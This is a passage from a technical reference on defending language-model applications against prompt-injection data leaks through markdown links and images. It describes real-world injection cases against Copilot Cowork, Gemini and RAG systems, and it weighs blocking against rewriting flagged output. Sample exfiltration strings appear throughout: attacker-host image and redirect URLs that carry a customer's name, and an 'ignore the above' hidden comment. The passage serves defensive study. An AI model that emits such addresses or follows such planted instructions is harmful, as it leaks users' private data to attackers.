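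1. The library rewrites automatic links such as `<https://reports.example/q3>` as ordinary links. It refuses them if the address contains HTML entities such as `&lt;`.
2. The parser remark reads the markdown, and the library converts the result into HTML.
3. DOMPurify removes tags and attributes that aren't on a list modelled on GitHub's. The library keeps only addresses that begin with a prefix the developer has permitted.
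4. Another tool, Turndown, converts the clean HTML back into markdown.
5. The library replaces characters that have a special meaning, such as brackets, with HTML entities wherever they occur in ordinary text.

The fifth step is the one that deals with the `div`. remark follows CommonMark, so the image is still text when DOMPurify sees it, and there is no `img` tag to check. DOMPurify drops the unlisted `markdown` attribute. The library then encodes the text, and `![Renewals](https://img.attacker.example/a.png)` should come out roughly like this:

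```
&#x21;&#x5b;Renewals&#x5d;&#x28;https&#x3a;&#x2f;&#x2f;img.attacker.example&#x2f;a.png&#x29;
```

A browser displays these codes as the original characters, but a markdown parser doesn't treat them as image brackets. Backslashes before the brackets would be shorter, but according to Socket, different parsers interpreted them differently.

However, people can hardly read the result until a program renders it. In this example, 47 characters become 92. The documentation therefore recommends the library only for markdown that a program will convert to a format such as HTML. A colleague who received the cleaned summary as a plain-text email would see the codes.

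Vercel Labs made the library for services including GitHub, but GitHub displays the entities unless the developer turns on a setting called `sanitizeForCommonmark`, which is off by default. With the setting on, the library encodes less and, as the documentation acknowledges, depends more on correct parsing, so developers who post to GitHub lose some of the protection that encoding provides.

If neither site in the manager's answer is on the list, the link and the chart become:

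```
[Full report](#)

![Renewals]()
```

The words "Full report" still look like a working link, but clicking them only takes the reader to the top of the current page. The image has an empty address. Neither the link nor the image has a notice like the "[blocked]" that *harden-react-markdown* adds.

The list of permitted prefixes has a gap of its own. Suppose the developer permits images from `https://assets.example/images/`, and the same site has a redirect page at `/leaving`. The following address begins with the permitted prefix:

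```
https://assets.example/images/../leaving?to=https://attacker.example/anna-berg
```

The two dots mean "go up one level", so the browser requests `https://assets.example/leaving`. The library doesn't resolve the dots, and its documentation leaves it to the developer's web server to refuse such paths. That advice doesn't help much with browsers, because they resolve the dots before sending the request and the server never receives them. A filter should resolve the address before comparing it with the list.

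The library also cuts off input beyond 100,000 characters by default, to protect against overload. It does this before parsing, so it still cleans everything it returns. But the end of a long report would be missing, and the documentation doesn't describe any notice to the reader.

To test the library, its developers collected markdown files designed to get a forbidden address past it. They clean each file, convert the result to HTML with five renderers (remark, marked, markdown-it, showdown and commonmark), and check whether the HTML is safe. These bypass tests make up 555 of the suite's more than 800 tests. Using several renderers is sensible because a trick that fails in one parser may work in another. But the five do not include GitHub's or GitLab's own renderers, and the tests cover only tricks that somebody has thought of. The developers call the library "brand new" and give no security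 guarantee.

### Carriers that only work on GitHub

In GitHub Agentic Workflows, a model's text becomes issues, comments and pull requests. Several kinds of text that are harmless in a chat window have a special meaning on GitHub. The table combines the treatments from GitHub's specification and its user documentation, *Safe Outputs*.

| The model's text | What can happen on GitHub | Neutralised form |
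|---|---|---|
| `@attacker` | GitHub notifies that user | `@ attacker` in the specification, backticks around the mention in the user documentation |
| `/close this issue` | A program that listens for commands closes the issue | `\/close this issue` |
| `owner/repo#456` | An entry appears in the timeline of another project's issue | Backticks around the reference, if the developer restricts references |
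| `https://attacker.example/r` | GitHub makes it a clickable link | `[URL redacted: unauthorized domain]` in the specification, `(redacted)` in the user documentation |
| `<!-- ignore the above -->` | Readers see nothing, but a model that reads the issue's source does | Removed |

The backslash before the command stops it from running without changing the text people see. A markdown renderer displays `\/close` as `/close`, but a program that checks whether the raw comment begins with a slash finds a backslash and does nothing.

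Mentions are harder because many of them are useful. A model that reports a bug should be able to notify the person who asked for the report. By default, GitHub permits mentions of the project's collaborators and of people already involved in the issue, and neutralises the rest. Programs that respond to their own names, such as `@copilot`, have a separate limit: the first ten mentions stay active, and the sanitiser puts backticks around the rest. This prevents large numbers of automatic tasks, but a single mention is enough to start a task. To prevent that too, a developer can set the limit to zero.

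To decide which mentions to permit, a program has to look up a project's collaborators and, for some projects, the members of a team. In May 2026, GitHub's specification required the sanitiser to compare each mention with a list. Version 1.29.8, dated 1 October, splits the work between two jobs. The job that runs the model has no credentials for the lookup and must leave mentions untouched. A trusted job checks them just before publication. The file passed between the two jobs therefore contains live mentions, which is safe because mentions do nothing until GitHub publishes them.

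GitHub's image proxy, Camo, requires signed image addresses, but this doesn't stop an attack through a published comment, because GitHub automatically signs the addresses of images in published text. If a model could post the manager's chart in a comment, GitHub would sign the chart's address, which contains Anna Berg's name, and Camo would pass the name to the attacker's server. On a public project, the attacker doesn't need an image, because anyone can read the comment. GitHub therefore also restricts, by default, the flow of data from private projects to public ones.

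### GitHub's order of checks

The specification requires seven steps in a fixed order for every operation that the model proposes:

1. Check that the operation has the right structure, and reject it if not.
2. Count the operations of each type, and reject the whole batch if there are more than the developer permits.
3. Sanitise all text, and reject the operation if the sanitiser finds unsafe content that it can't clean.
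4. If the developer has set an allowlist, redact the address of every link and image that isn't on it.
5. Check that the model may write to the chosen project, and reject the operation if not.
6. Replace temporary references with real issue numbers, and reject the operation if one is missing.
7. Send the operation to GitHub, which creates the issue or comment.

Only steps 3 and 4 rewrite text. A comment loses only the link when an address is outside the allowlist. The whole comment is rejected if its destination project is wrong, because rewriting the text can't fix that. A rejection in steps 3 to 6 stops only the operation concerned, and the rest of the batch continues.

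Some limits apply earlier, while the model is still working. A comment may contain at most 65,536 characters, ten mentions and 50 links. If the model exceeds a limit, it receives an error with the limit and a suggested correction, so it can try again. This makes rejection less disruptive than in a chat, where the manager would simply get an error message. The trusted job repeats the check in case someone has tampered with the file. Error code E008 means both "too many links" and "unsafe content that can't be cleaned", so an investigator can't tell from the code alone which happened.

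For the details of step 3, the specification refers to its section 9.2, but that section is about something else. GitHub describes the sanitiser in sections 6.4 and 9.4, and the two lists differ:

| | Section 6.4 | Section 9.4 |
|---|---|---|
| Invisible characters | Removes zero-width and most control characters | Removes null bytes |
| Addresses | Checks every address in the text | Checks inline links, automatic links and inline images |
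| Mentions and commands | Neutralises both | No rule for either |
| HTML | Removes comments, turns unsafe tags into visible text | Optionally removes `script`, `iframe`, `object` and `embed` tags, and attributes such as `onerror` |

A developer who implemented only section 9.4 would miss reference-style images, which EchoLeak used, and raw `img` tags. Section 6.4 covers both because it applies to addresses in any notation.

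The order of the steps in section 6.4 also matters. The first step is to remove invisible characters, because an attacker could put one in the middle of `javascript:`. If the sanitiser checked the address type first, it wouldn't recognise the word, and removing the character later would produce a working `javascript:` address.

The notice that replaces an address is itself markdown, and GitHub parses it again. Under section 9.4, the manager's link would become this:

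```
[Full report]([URL redacted: unauthorized domain])
```

The address part now contains spaces, so CommonMark doesn't treat it as a link, and readers see the brackets. But an attacker can define the notice as a label, as with `[https]`. If the answer contains the line `[URL redacted: unauthorized domain]: https://attacker.example/r`, the notice becomes a link to the attacker's site. Redacting the address in that line too, as in Section 6.4, prevents this. If a program replaces the address with the shorter `(redacted)`, the result is `[Full report]((redacted))`, a valid link to a page called "(redacted)" on the current site.

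Both sections exempt code from at least some of their rules, which leaves samples like the manager's logo intact. The exemption is safe only if the sanitiser and GitHub parse code as beginning and ending in the same places. An attacker would look for text that the sanitiser parses as code but GitHub doesn't.

GitHub's user documentation shows one case where the two are bound to differ. A model can attach an HTML file to an issue, and backticks don't mark code in HTML. The sanitiser therefore checks every address in these files, including those between backticks, even if the developer has exempted code elsewhere.

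GitHub can also run a separate detector that looks for signs of an attack in the proposed operations. In its warning mode, the response depends on what the operation does:

- Issues, comments and other text that people can review still appear, with a prominent warning.
- A change to an existing branch of code becomes a pull request, which someone has to accept.
- Operations such as merging code, closing an issue or adding a label don't go ahead.

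The warning includes an HTML comment as a marker for other programs. The model can't forge this marker because the sanitiser removes all HTML comments from the model's text.

### A message that leaks when someone opens it

Microsoft's Copilot Cowork works through tasks across a user's files, email and chats. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* describes an attack in which the dangerous text never appeared in Cowork at all:

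1. The user added a skill to Cowork, which is a file of instructions for a certain kind of task. Five of its 81 lines were the attacker's.
2. The user asked for a review of the week's work, and Cowork used the skill.
3. The attacker's lines claimed that a service could create previews of the documents. Cowork fetched a download link for each file and put the links into the addresses of images on the attacker's server.
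4. Cowork sent the review to the user as a Teams message, with the images in it.
5. The user opened Teams, which loaded the images. The attacker received the download links and could fetch the files.

According to Microsoft's documentation, Cowork asks for permission before it sends an email or a Teams message. It didn't ask when the recipient was the user. A message to the user can still be dangerous, even though users may read their own files, because the program that displays it can contact a third party. PromptArmor demonstrated this attack in Teams and states that messages opened in Outlook can also trigger requests to a third party. *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* (Willison, 2026) describes the same problem for messages in the user's own inbox.

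The user had little chance of noticing. Cowork listed the Teams message among its actions but didn't show its contents, even when the user clicked on it. Cowork can also run such reviews on a schedule, with nobody watching.

Each leaked download link worked without a login, so an address of ordinary length was enough to expose a whole document. A filter that searched outgoing messages for names or figures from the documents would have found none.

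The attack succeeded in all five of PromptArmor's trials, at first with a setting that chose between Claude Opus 4.7 and Claude Sonnet 4.6. The same text also worked with Opus 4.7 alone, which searched more thoroughly and leaked more documents. Five trials are too few to estimate the success rate precisely, but they show that the attack didn't depend on a weak model.

Teams rendered the message, so sanitising Cowork's own display would not have helped. Microsoft could remove external images from messages before Cowork sends them, or stop Teams and Outlook from loading images in messages that Cowork wrote. Removing the images also protects recipients who use another company's mail program. An approval step would help only if it showed the image addresses, because the message text could look like a normal weekly review.

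PromptArmor regards the problem as a risk of the product's design rather than a single bug, and suggests that administrators block downloads from SharePoint, where their company keeps its files, so that Cowork can't obtain the links. Users can then view the affected files only in a browser, and can't print them, synchronise them or open them in Word or Excel. The images in a message would still load, and an attacker could ask for a sentence from a document instead of a link to it.

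## When is rewriting better than rejecting the whole output?

If the application acts before the browser requests the image, it can stop the leak by either removing the chart from the sales manager's answer or withholding the whole answer. Removing only the chart lets the manager read the rest of the text. Rewriting is better when most flagged answers are harmless and a false sentence in the remaining text would do limited damage. Blocking is better when a flag is strong evidence of an attack, when manipulated text could do serious harm, or when the link, image or HTML would be useless once rewritten.

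### The case for blocking

The chart got into the answer because the model followed an attacker's instructions. The same instructions could also have made the model change 84 per cent to 48 or leave out a paragraph about lost customers, and removing the chart wouldn't correct either error.

Tenable showed how text and a link can work together in an attack on Gemini Cloud Assist, which explains log entries to people who run software on Google's cloud. Its researchers sent a request to a test service with instructions in the field that normally identifies the browser, and the service logged them. When a simulated victim asked Gemini to explain the log entry, the explanation contained the researchers' message and a phishing link. In response, Google stopped rendering links in log summaries, so readers now see the markdown source. This prevents accidental clicks, but if another injection succeeded,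 the administrator would still read the message and could copy the address.

Text without links can also be false. *DenialRAG* (2026) studied an attack on retrieval-augmented generation (RAG), in which a system looks up documents and gives them to the model along with the question. The attacker plants a single document that names the correct answer, denies it, and explains why a different answer is right. In tests on eight models from four vendors, the denial was the most influential part of the document. If the assistant repeated such a denial, a manager who remembered the true renewal rate might dismiss the memory as a common mistake.

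These attacks are a good reason to distrust a manipulated answer, but they only partly support blocking. An attacker who only wants to deceive the manager doesn't need a link, so a link filter would deliver the false answer whether it rewrites or blocks. An attacker who wants data has a reason to leave the text alone, because a strange answer attracts attention. An image that carries stolen data therefore shows that someone manipulated the model, but it is weaker evidence that the surrounding text is false. In phishing, however, the text usually has to mislead the reader into clicking.

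A colleague's software can restore a defanged address to its normal form, and so can a language model that later reads the conversation. Blocking the whole output also avoids this risk, but so does removing just the address, so the risk is specific to defanging.

### False alarms and denial of service

Attacks are rare and detectors make mistakes, so most flagged answers may be harmless. Unit 42, the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, compared the content filters of several AI platforms and found that highly sensitive ones frequently classified harmless queries as threats. Code review requests were often misclassified. The manager's logo sample could easily cause the same kind of mistake in a link filter, although the filters Unit 42 compared were not link filters.

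Blocking also lets outsiders suppress answers. Suppose an assistant withholds every answer that contains a link to a known malicious site. Someone who dislikes a product could put such a link in a public review of it, without any hidden instructions, and the assistant would withhold any answer that copied the link. If the assistant rewrote the output instead, readers would lose only the link.

The closest published tests attack safety classifiers and the models' own refusals. Zhang, Xiong and Mao (2024), in *LLM Safeguard is a Double-Edged Sword*, targeted Llama Guard 3, a separate model that labels conversations as safe or unsafe. Adding about 30 characters of text made it reject over 97 per cent of harmless requests. But they had access to the classifier's parameters and assumed the attacker could insert the text into the user's requests, for example by tampering with a configuration file.

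An attacker who plants a document needs less access. *Machine Against the RAG* (2024) showed that one document could make a RAG system refuse to answer a question of the attacker's choice, though the most effective documents were easy to detect. In *Hoist with His Own Petard*, Suo, Shang and colleagues (2025) planted texts that diverted the model to a forbidden request, which it then refused. With GPT-4, this worked for 79 per cent of the targeted questions in the HotpotQA test collection and 25 per cent of those in Natural Questions.

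Newer models resist that method better. *When Safety Becomes a Vulnerability* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) reports that it worked in 5.6 per cent of cases on GPT-5.2 with Natural Questions, and in none after a filter had removed suspected injections. The paper also introduces a stronger attack that contains no instructions. The planted document presents the subject of the question as a legal or safety risk, which leads the model to decline. Across nine models and three collections, this attack's success rate after filtering was 67.3 per cent higher, in relative terms, than the average of the best earlier attacks.

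Rewriting the output wouldn't help against any of these attacks, because the refusal comes before there is an answer to rewrite. But the attacks show that a component that can refuse is a target. A link filter that blocks whole outputs would probably be an easier target than a model, since a single bad address is enough to trigger it.

Such refusals can also persist. Frichette, in *[Deprecated] Claude Magic String Denial of Service*, describes a test string that Anthropic published so that developers could check how their applications handle refusals. Anyone who got the string into a document, log or shared chat that Claude read could stop Claude from answering. If the application kept the text in the conversation history, every later request failed too. Anthropic had patched this by May 2026. A link filter that blocks the whole output could cause the same problem, because the quarterly report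 stays in the conversation and may lead the model to output another image when the manager asks the next question.

### A rule for choosing

The following rule is this reference's own model, and all its numbers are invented. It compares the two policies for flagged outputs only, using four quantities:

- *q* is the share of flagged outputs that are malicious.
- *V* is the value of a clean answer.
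- *v* is the part of that value that rewriting destroys.
- *H* is the expected harm of delivering a manipulated answer after rewriting.

Blocking delivers nothing, so its value is zero. Rewriting gains *V* − *v* for each harmless answer and costs *H* for each malicious one. On average, rewriting is better than blocking if

(1 − *q*)(*V* − *v*) > *qH*.

The harm *H* doesn't include the leak that rewriting prevents. Malicious outputs that the detector misses reach the user under both policies, so they don't affect the comparison.

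Suppose an assistant writes 100,000 answers, of which 100 are malicious. The detector catches 95 of these and also flags 2 per cent of the 99,900 harmless answers, which is 1,998. Only 95 of the 2,093 flagged answers are malicious, so *q* is about 4.5 per cent. If a clean answer is worth 1 and rewriting destroys 0.2 of that, rewriting wins as long as

*H* < (1,998 × 0.8) / 95 ≈ 16.8.

If a clean answer saves the manager five minutes, a manipulated one would have to cost more than about 84 minutes before blocking became the better policy. The limit changes considerably with the detector:

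| False positive rate | Harmless answers flagged | Malicious share of flagged answers | Rewriting wins if *H* is below |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2% | 1,998 | 4.5% | 16.8 |
| 0.5% | About 500 | 16% | 4.2 |
| 0.1% | About 100 | 49% | 0.84 |

A more precise detector therefore strengthens the case for blocking. With the detector in the last row, nearly half of the flagged answers are malicious, and blocking discards few good ones.

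The frequency of attacks matters just as much. If 1,000 of the 100,000 answers were malicious and the detector still caught 95 per cent of them, the limit for the 2 per cent detector would fall from 16.8 to about 1.7. A jump in the number of flags may mean that more answers are malicious, but an outsider who wants to deny service can also cause one. If planted links put flags on 5,000 answers whose text is sound, the limit rises to about 58, so the application should keep rewriting. Staff therefore have to check some of the flagged answers before deciding whether the application should start blocking.

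A developer can collect such a sample before choosing a policy. AWS's *Options for handling harmful content detected by Amazon Bedrock Guardrails* describes a detect mode, in which the filter reports what it found but takes no action. This mode leaves dangerous links intact, so a developer should use invented customer data when testing a link filter with it.

### Retrying and human review

An application that rejects an answer can ask the model for another one. The manager then waits longer but may get a complete answer with working links. Suppose a retry never delivers a manipulated answer and, when the flagged answer was harmless, preserves a value *R* after a deduction for the wait. Rewriting is then better only if (1 − *q*)(*V* − *v* − *R*) > *qH*. With the 2 per cent detector and *R* = 0.6, the limit on *H* falls from 16.8 to 4.2. If *R* is at least 0.8, retrying is better however small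 *H* is.

The assumption that a retry is never manipulated is weak, because the model may follow the same instructions when it reads the same quarterly report again. Each retry also gives the attacker another chance to get past the filter. Suppose every attempt is malicious and the filter misses 5 per cent of them, independently. An application that makes up to three attempts and delivers the first one to pass will deliver a malicious answer in 1 − 0.95³ ≈ 14 per cent of cases.

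Anthropic's *Handle streaming refusals* gives similar advice for cases where a safety classifier stops Claude mid-answer. Resending the same request to the same model usually leads to another refusal, so it recommends removing or rephrasing the message that caused the refusal, clearing the history, or trying another model. Another model might still follow instructions hidden in the report, so for injections it is more useful to change the message or clear the history.

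The manager asked for a summary of the report that contains the instructions, so the application can't leave the report out. It could instead repeat the request without giving the model access to customer records. The new answer might still contain a false figure, but it couldn't reveal a name that appears only in those records.

Human review keeps all the good answers if the reviewer makes no mistakes. Its value per flagged answer is (1 − *q*)*V* − *c*, where *c* is the cost of a review. This is better than rewriting if

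*c* < (1 − *q*)*v* + *qH*.

With the 2 per cent detector and *H* = 10, a review is worthwhile if the effort it takes is below about 0.64, or a little over three minutes in the earlier example. At three minutes each, reviewing the 2,093 flagged answers would take about 105 hours. The 0.1 per cent detector would reduce this to about 10 hours.

The reviewer might also stop looking carefully, because only one in every 22 flagged answers would be malicious. A reviewer can check in seconds whether an address contains a customer's name, but has to open the report to check whether renewals rose to 84 per cent. A reviewer who isn't the manager also needs permission to read the report.

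### Graded responses

Large products don't have to apply one policy to every flag. In Gemini, Tenable saw redirected links, truncated outputs and outright refusals.

Tenable doesn't explain how Gemini chose among them, but the combination makes sense under the rule. Google can redirect every link because doing so removes little of value, whereas refusing loses the whole answer and so requires better evidence. Truncation is harder to justify, because a summary that ends early may give the good news and omit the reservations. A truncated summary needs a visible notice for the same reasons a removed link does.

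AWS also lets developers choose, for each type of personal data, whether to block the whole response or mask the item with a label such as `{NAME}`, as described in *Remove PII from conversations by using sensitive information filters*. AWS suggests blocking for an assistant that answers general questions from public documents, and masking for one that summarises conversations between customers and service staff.

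A customer's name should not appear in an answer drawn from public documents, so its presence suggests that something went wrong. But a name is normal in a summary of a customer's phone call, and blocking every answer that contains one would make the product useless.

The address check described in OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) also has graded responses. ChatGPT either asks the user, or blocks the transmission and has the agent try another way. Blocking stops only that operation, so the user may still get a complete answer.

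OpenAI compares the agent to a customer service employee who can give refunds. Some customers will lie, so the company limits the size of refunds instead of relying on the employee to spot every lie. Similarly, an application can reduce *H* by limiting what a manipulated model can do, which makes rewriting safer even if the detector doesn't improve.

### The rule in four situations

The table applies the rule to four kinds of carrier, again with invented values.

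| Situation | *q* | *V* − *v* | Limit on *H* | Assumed *H* | Better policy |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Link in a chat answer with citations | 4.5% | 0.8 | 16.8 | 3 | Rewrite |
| Image whose address contains a customer's name | 90% | 0.9 | 0.1 | 3 | Reject, then retry without the customer records |
| Address passed to a tool | 4.5% | 0 | 0 | 3 | Reject the tool call |
| Public post | 4.5% | 0.8 | 16.8 | 50 | Hold for review |

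**A chat answer with citations** is usually still useful without one link. The manager can compare the figure with the report, especially if the application shows the defanged address. The value of links also affects how much risk a company accepts. Gemini doesn't render external images, but Checkmarx reported in October 2025 that clickable links could still leak data. Google closed that report as "Won't Fix (Infeasible)" and, according to Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents*, said the issue wasn't severe enough to track as a security bug. For medical or financial instructions, *H* could be far above 3, and an assistant that gives them should block more readily.

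In the table, a zero-click image leads to blocking because its address contains a customer's name in the query, which few harmless images have. A filter that removes every external image, as Gemini's does, acts without such evidence. If only one removed image in a thousand were malicious, the limit on *H* would be about 900, and rejecting every answer with an image would be unreasonable.

A second image could also have got past the filter. In the earlier example, two images each carry the name, and the filter has a 90 per cent chance of catching each one. If it has caught at least one, there is an 18 per cent chance that it missed the other. With a leak weighted at 50, that adds about 9 to *H*, which alone exceeds the limit for the 0.1 per cent detector but not for the 2 per cent detector.

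**An address passed to a tool** is useful only if it works. If the assistant tries to open a web page and the application changes the address to `[https]://reports[.]example/q3`, the tool can't open it. Stripping the query may be worse, because the tool could open the wrong page without an error and the model would summarise it. The application should reject the call and tell the model why.

Claude's page-fetching tool can reject an address without ending the task. According to Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, it returns an error code, such as `url_too_long` for an address of more than 250 characters, inside an otherwise successful response, so Claude can continue. But rejection only stops addresses that the rule forbids. The nested-link attack that Willison described succeeded because the rule permitted every address.

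The check has to happen where the tool runs. AWS's filter for personal data doesn't examine the arguments of tool calls, so an email address that it would mask in an answer reaches the tool unchanged. Many tools don't check their arguments properly either. In *ToFu*, Ananto, Prevost-Avenel and colleagues (2026) tested 3,405 tools on 273 servers that use the Model Context Protocol, a common way of connecting models to tools, and found verified bugs in 343 tools on 118 servers. They also showed that an attacker can get a model to repeat text formatted as a tool call, and all six agent frameworks they tried treated it as a real call. A filter that treats such text as part of the answer would miss the call.

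A public post can mislead many people before anyone corrects it. If a false statement does 0.5 of harm to each reader, *H* is 50 for 100 readers, which makes rewriting the worse choice, but only 5 for ten readers, which makes it the better one. A post can usually wait an hour, so holding it for review does less harm than in a chat, where the manager is left with an empty screen. GitHub's rule of publishing reviewable text with a warning is a reasonable alternative for a small project whose members will read the comment anyway.

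Links also need stricter treatment in posts and messages than in a chat window, because link previews can send out data contained in the address without anyone clicking. PromptArmor reports that the agent OpenClaw is exposed to this by default when used through Telegram. Defanging the address before posting prevents the preview, as long as nothing later turns it back into a working link. But if the post announces a new web page, readers need a working link, which a reviewer can provide after approving the address.

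## Should neutralisation be on by default, and how useful is the output afterwards?

Neutralisation should be on by default, because people notice a missing link sooner than a missing defence. If the application neutralises the link to `reports.example` by default, the sales manager complains and the developer adds the site to the allowlist. If it permits everything by default, someone can hide instructions in a quarterly report and leak a customer's name without anyone noticing. Neutralisation does make some harmless answers less useful, and how much less depends on whether a person, a program or another model reads them.

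### Always on, opt-out and opt-in

Some filters always rewrite the text. Opt-out filters rewrite it unless the developer turns them off. Opt-in filters report what they find and leave the text alone unless the developer asks for a change.

One library can combine these designs. *harden-react-markdown* always blocks `javascript:` links, which makes sense because nobody needs one in a summary. For ordinary addresses, its filtering is opt-out, so it blocks every link and image until the developer lists permitted prefixes, and the entry `"*"` turns this filtering off.

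A strict default can backfire. A developer who sees "[blocked]" after every link in the first test may enter `"*"` for links and images alike, and the chart then loads. But the two lists are separate, so the developer can open one and leave the other closed:

```tsx
<HardenedMarkdown
  defaultOrigin="https://app.example"
  allowedLinkPrefixes={["*"]}
>
  {answer}
</HardenedMarkdown>
```

All ordinary web links now work, and the library still blocks every image. This is a reasonable setting for an assistant that searches the web, although an attacker could still use a link if the manager clicks it.

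### What the caller receives from a tool that only reports

Guardrails AI makes a library that checks model output with validators, each of which tests for one kind of problem. The developer chooses what happens when a validator finds a problem. According to Guardrails AI's *Use on_fail actions*, the default is `noop` ("no operation"). In its example, a validator for personal data checks a sentence containing John Doe's name and email address. `validation_passed` is `False`, but `validated_output` is identical to the original text.

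Suppose that a developer uses a validator for unsafe images in the same way:

```python
result = guard.validate(answer)
show(result.validated_output)
```

This code runs a check and then displays something called "validated output", so a colleague reviewing it could easily believe it was safe. It displays the chart, and the browser sends Anna Berg's name to the attacker. The application has to test `validation_passed` first, or the developer has to choose another action. Guardrails AI offers several:

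| Action | What the caller receives |
|---|---|
| `noop` (the default) | The original text and a failed check |
| `fix` | A corrected text, if the validator can produce one |
| `filter` | Structured output without the field that failed |
| `refrain` | No output |
| `exception` | An error |
| `reask` | A new answer from the model |
| `fix_reask` | A corrected text, or a new answer if the corrected text fails the check too |

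Some of these have side effects that matter for links. In the documented example, `validation_passed` is `True` after a `fix`, so an administrator who counted attacks by looking for `False` would miss every one that the validator repaired.

The error raised by `exception` contains the whole offending sentence, including John Doe's email address. If an application rendered that error as markdown, the rejected image could still load. The application should show a fixed message and keep the details in a restricted log.

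A developer can also write a custom action, such as one that defangs addresses. The function receives the text and the positions of the problems. In the documented output, the positions cover John Doe's name but not his email address, although `fix` masks both. A function that changed only the reported positions would leave the email address in the text.

Amazon's cloud service, AWS, offers a similar choice. Its *GuardrailPiiEntity* lists `BLOCK`, `ANONYMIZE` and `NONE` as the possible actions for personal data, with separate settings for input and output. `NONE` corresponds to detect mode, which reports findings in the trace, a record that accompanies the response. Developers can also disable the input check, which avoids the charge but produces no findings.

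AWS extended the choice between blocking and masking to both prompts and responses (*Amazon Bedrock Guardrails announces new capabilities to safely build generative AI applications*, 2025). It also accepts regular expressions for text that its built-in types don't cover. A developer could write one to mask markdown images, but it would need to cover reference-style images too.

NVIDIA recommends a stricter response for NeMo Guardrails, its toolkit for checking model output. When an injection rule matches, the toolkit can reject the output or omit the matching text. NVIDIA calls rejection the safest action and the most appropriate for production. This is good advice for the code injections its rules look for, because deleting part of a program can leave something dangerous. If a filter deletes `<script>` once from `<scr<script>ipt>`, the remaining characters form a new `<script>` tag. The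 advice is less convincing for a summary with one bad link, because the rest of the text doesn't depend on the link.

Reporting without rewriting is useful during a trial, or when the caller is a program that needs the original text. A library can't detect whether its caller will display the text, but it could return the neutralised version as `safe_text` and the original as `unsafe_original`, so that a developer in a hurry would probably display the right one.

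### An empty list can permit everything or nothing

Developers also have to find out what a default means. An empty list, written `[]`, has opposite effects in different products:

| Setting | Effect of `[]` |
|---|---|
| `allowedLinkPrefixes` in *harden-react-markdown* | Refuses every link |
| `allowed-domains` in GitHub's specification | Permits every domain |
| `allowed-github-references` in GitHub's user documentation | Neutralises every reference to an issue, whereas leaving the setting out permits all of them |

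The second row comes from version 1.21.0 of the specification for Agentic Workflows, which GitHub published in May 2026. Other cleaning steps, such as removing `javascript:` addresses and neutralising commands, always run. Permitting every domain seems inconsistent with the specification's principle that "defaults favor security over convenience".

GitHub's user documentation describes a different default, in which the sanitiser permits only GitHub's own domains unless the developer adds others, and replaces all other addresses with `(redacted)`. According to GitHub's *Network Permissions*, the list of sites the model may contact also determines which addresses are kept in its text. By default, that list contains GitHub and some basic infrastructure, such as package servers.

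If the assistant posts its summary on GitHub, the manager's source link and the chart's address stay according to the May specification but are removed according to the user documentation. A developer should post a test comment with an outside link and an outside image instead of relying on either description.

Because one list serves several purposes, a developer who lets the model download packages from a site also permits links to that site. GitHub also uses the `allowed-domains` list to clean issues before the model reads them. If `reports.example` isn't on the list, the model sees `(redacted)` instead of the report's address and can't cite it. Adding the site lets the model cite the report, but it also lets the model read any `reports.example` address that an outsider has put in an issue.

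GitHub keeps the firewall around the model separate from the filter on links in the model's text. If a developer disables the firewall to fix a failed download, the filter still checks links against the site list.

### How an optional setting can skip a step

Each optional setting is a chance for the sanitiser to behave differently. Suppose a sanitiser normally neutralises all mentions, and a developer asks for an exception for colleagues. A programmer might add it like this:

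```python
def clean(text, allowed_mentions=None):
    if allowed_mentions is None:
        return standard_clean(text)
    return clean_with_mentions(text, allowed_mentions)
```

The second function begins as a copy of the first. If someone later adds a step for HTML comments to `standard_clean` but forgets the copy, an application that permits a single colleague's name will also let HTML comments through, even though the two are unrelated. GitHub's pull request 28049 concerned a fault of this kind, in which an optional setting created a second code path that missed some neutralisation steps.

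It is safer to have one function that always runs every step and to pass the list only to the step that handles mentions:

```python
def clean(text, allowed_mentions=()):
    text = remove_invisible_characters(text)
    text = filter_addresses(text)
    text = neutralise_commands(text)
    text = neutralise_mentions(text, except_for=allowed_mentions)
    return remove_html_comments(text)
```

Tests should cover combinations of settings, because testing only the default would have missed the fault. Four on/off settings have 16 combinations, few enough to run every hostile sample through all of them. The tests can also check that changing the mention setting never changes what happens to an image.

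### A person, a program and a second model

The sales manager wants to check the 84 per cent against the report. If the allowlist contains `reports.example`, the link works and only the attacker's chart is missing. If the list is empty, the manager gets the figure without a working link to its source. If users checked citations as often as participants did in Ding and colleagues' experiment, a filter that wrongly disabled the citations in 1,000 answers would prevent roughly 100 checks, unless the application showed the defanged addresses.

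A program may fail without any sign of trouble. Suppose that the company collects the sources of all its assistant's answers with this search pattern:

```
https?://[^\s)"]+
```

In the original answer, the pattern finds the report, the chart and the logo. If the application defangs the link and the chart but leaves code unchanged, the pattern finds only `https://assets.example/logo.png`. The program then records the logo as the answer's only source and reports no error.

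The developer could make the program recognise and restore defanged addresses. But if the program also opens each address to check that it works, it will send Anna Berg's name to `img.attacker.example`, and defanging will only have delayed the leak.

Programs are better served by a separate field than by addresses picked out of prose. Agentic Workflows has an optional `data` field for this purpose, which GitHub describes as a channel that survives sanitisation. The model's answer could include:

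```json
{"source": "https://reports.example/q3"}
```

GitHub adds the data to the published text as a code block, so people can read it too. The developer can prescribe which fields the data must have, but an injected model could still put the attacker's address in the `source` field. GitHub recommends that programs reading the data later check who wrote the comment and validate the value before using it. The program that collects sources should compare each address with its own allowlist.

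A second model may read the answer to turn it into an email, translate it, or answer the manager's next question. It can misinterpret a marker, for example by telling colleagues that access to the full report is blocked. It can also restore a defanged address. Models were trained on many reports in which analysts write `hxxps`, and an instruction such as "make the sources clickable" can lead them to change it back.

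Before relying on defanged text in a chain of models, a developer can measure how often the second model restores the addresses. The developer gives it answers containing defanged addresses on a server they control, sets ordinary tasks such as translating, tidying up and listing sources, and counts how many outputs contain a working address. If none do in 100 independent trials, the true rate could still be about 3 per cent, because a model with that rate would have a 0.97¹⁰⁰ ≈ 5 per cent chance of restoring none.

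The application should also neutralise the second model's output just before displaying it, whatever the test shows. A filter that runs only after the first model won't catch a chart that the second model restores.

### Double rewriting and accidental refanging

When several programs handle the same text, each may add its own protection. So GitHub's sanitiser, like Grimminck's rule, must change nothing when it runs on the same text again. For example, it skips names that already have backticks around them.

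Simple replacement rules often fail this test. A program that replaces every dot in a host name with `[.]` changes `reports.example` as follows:

```
Once:   reports[.]example
Twice:  reports[[.]]example
```

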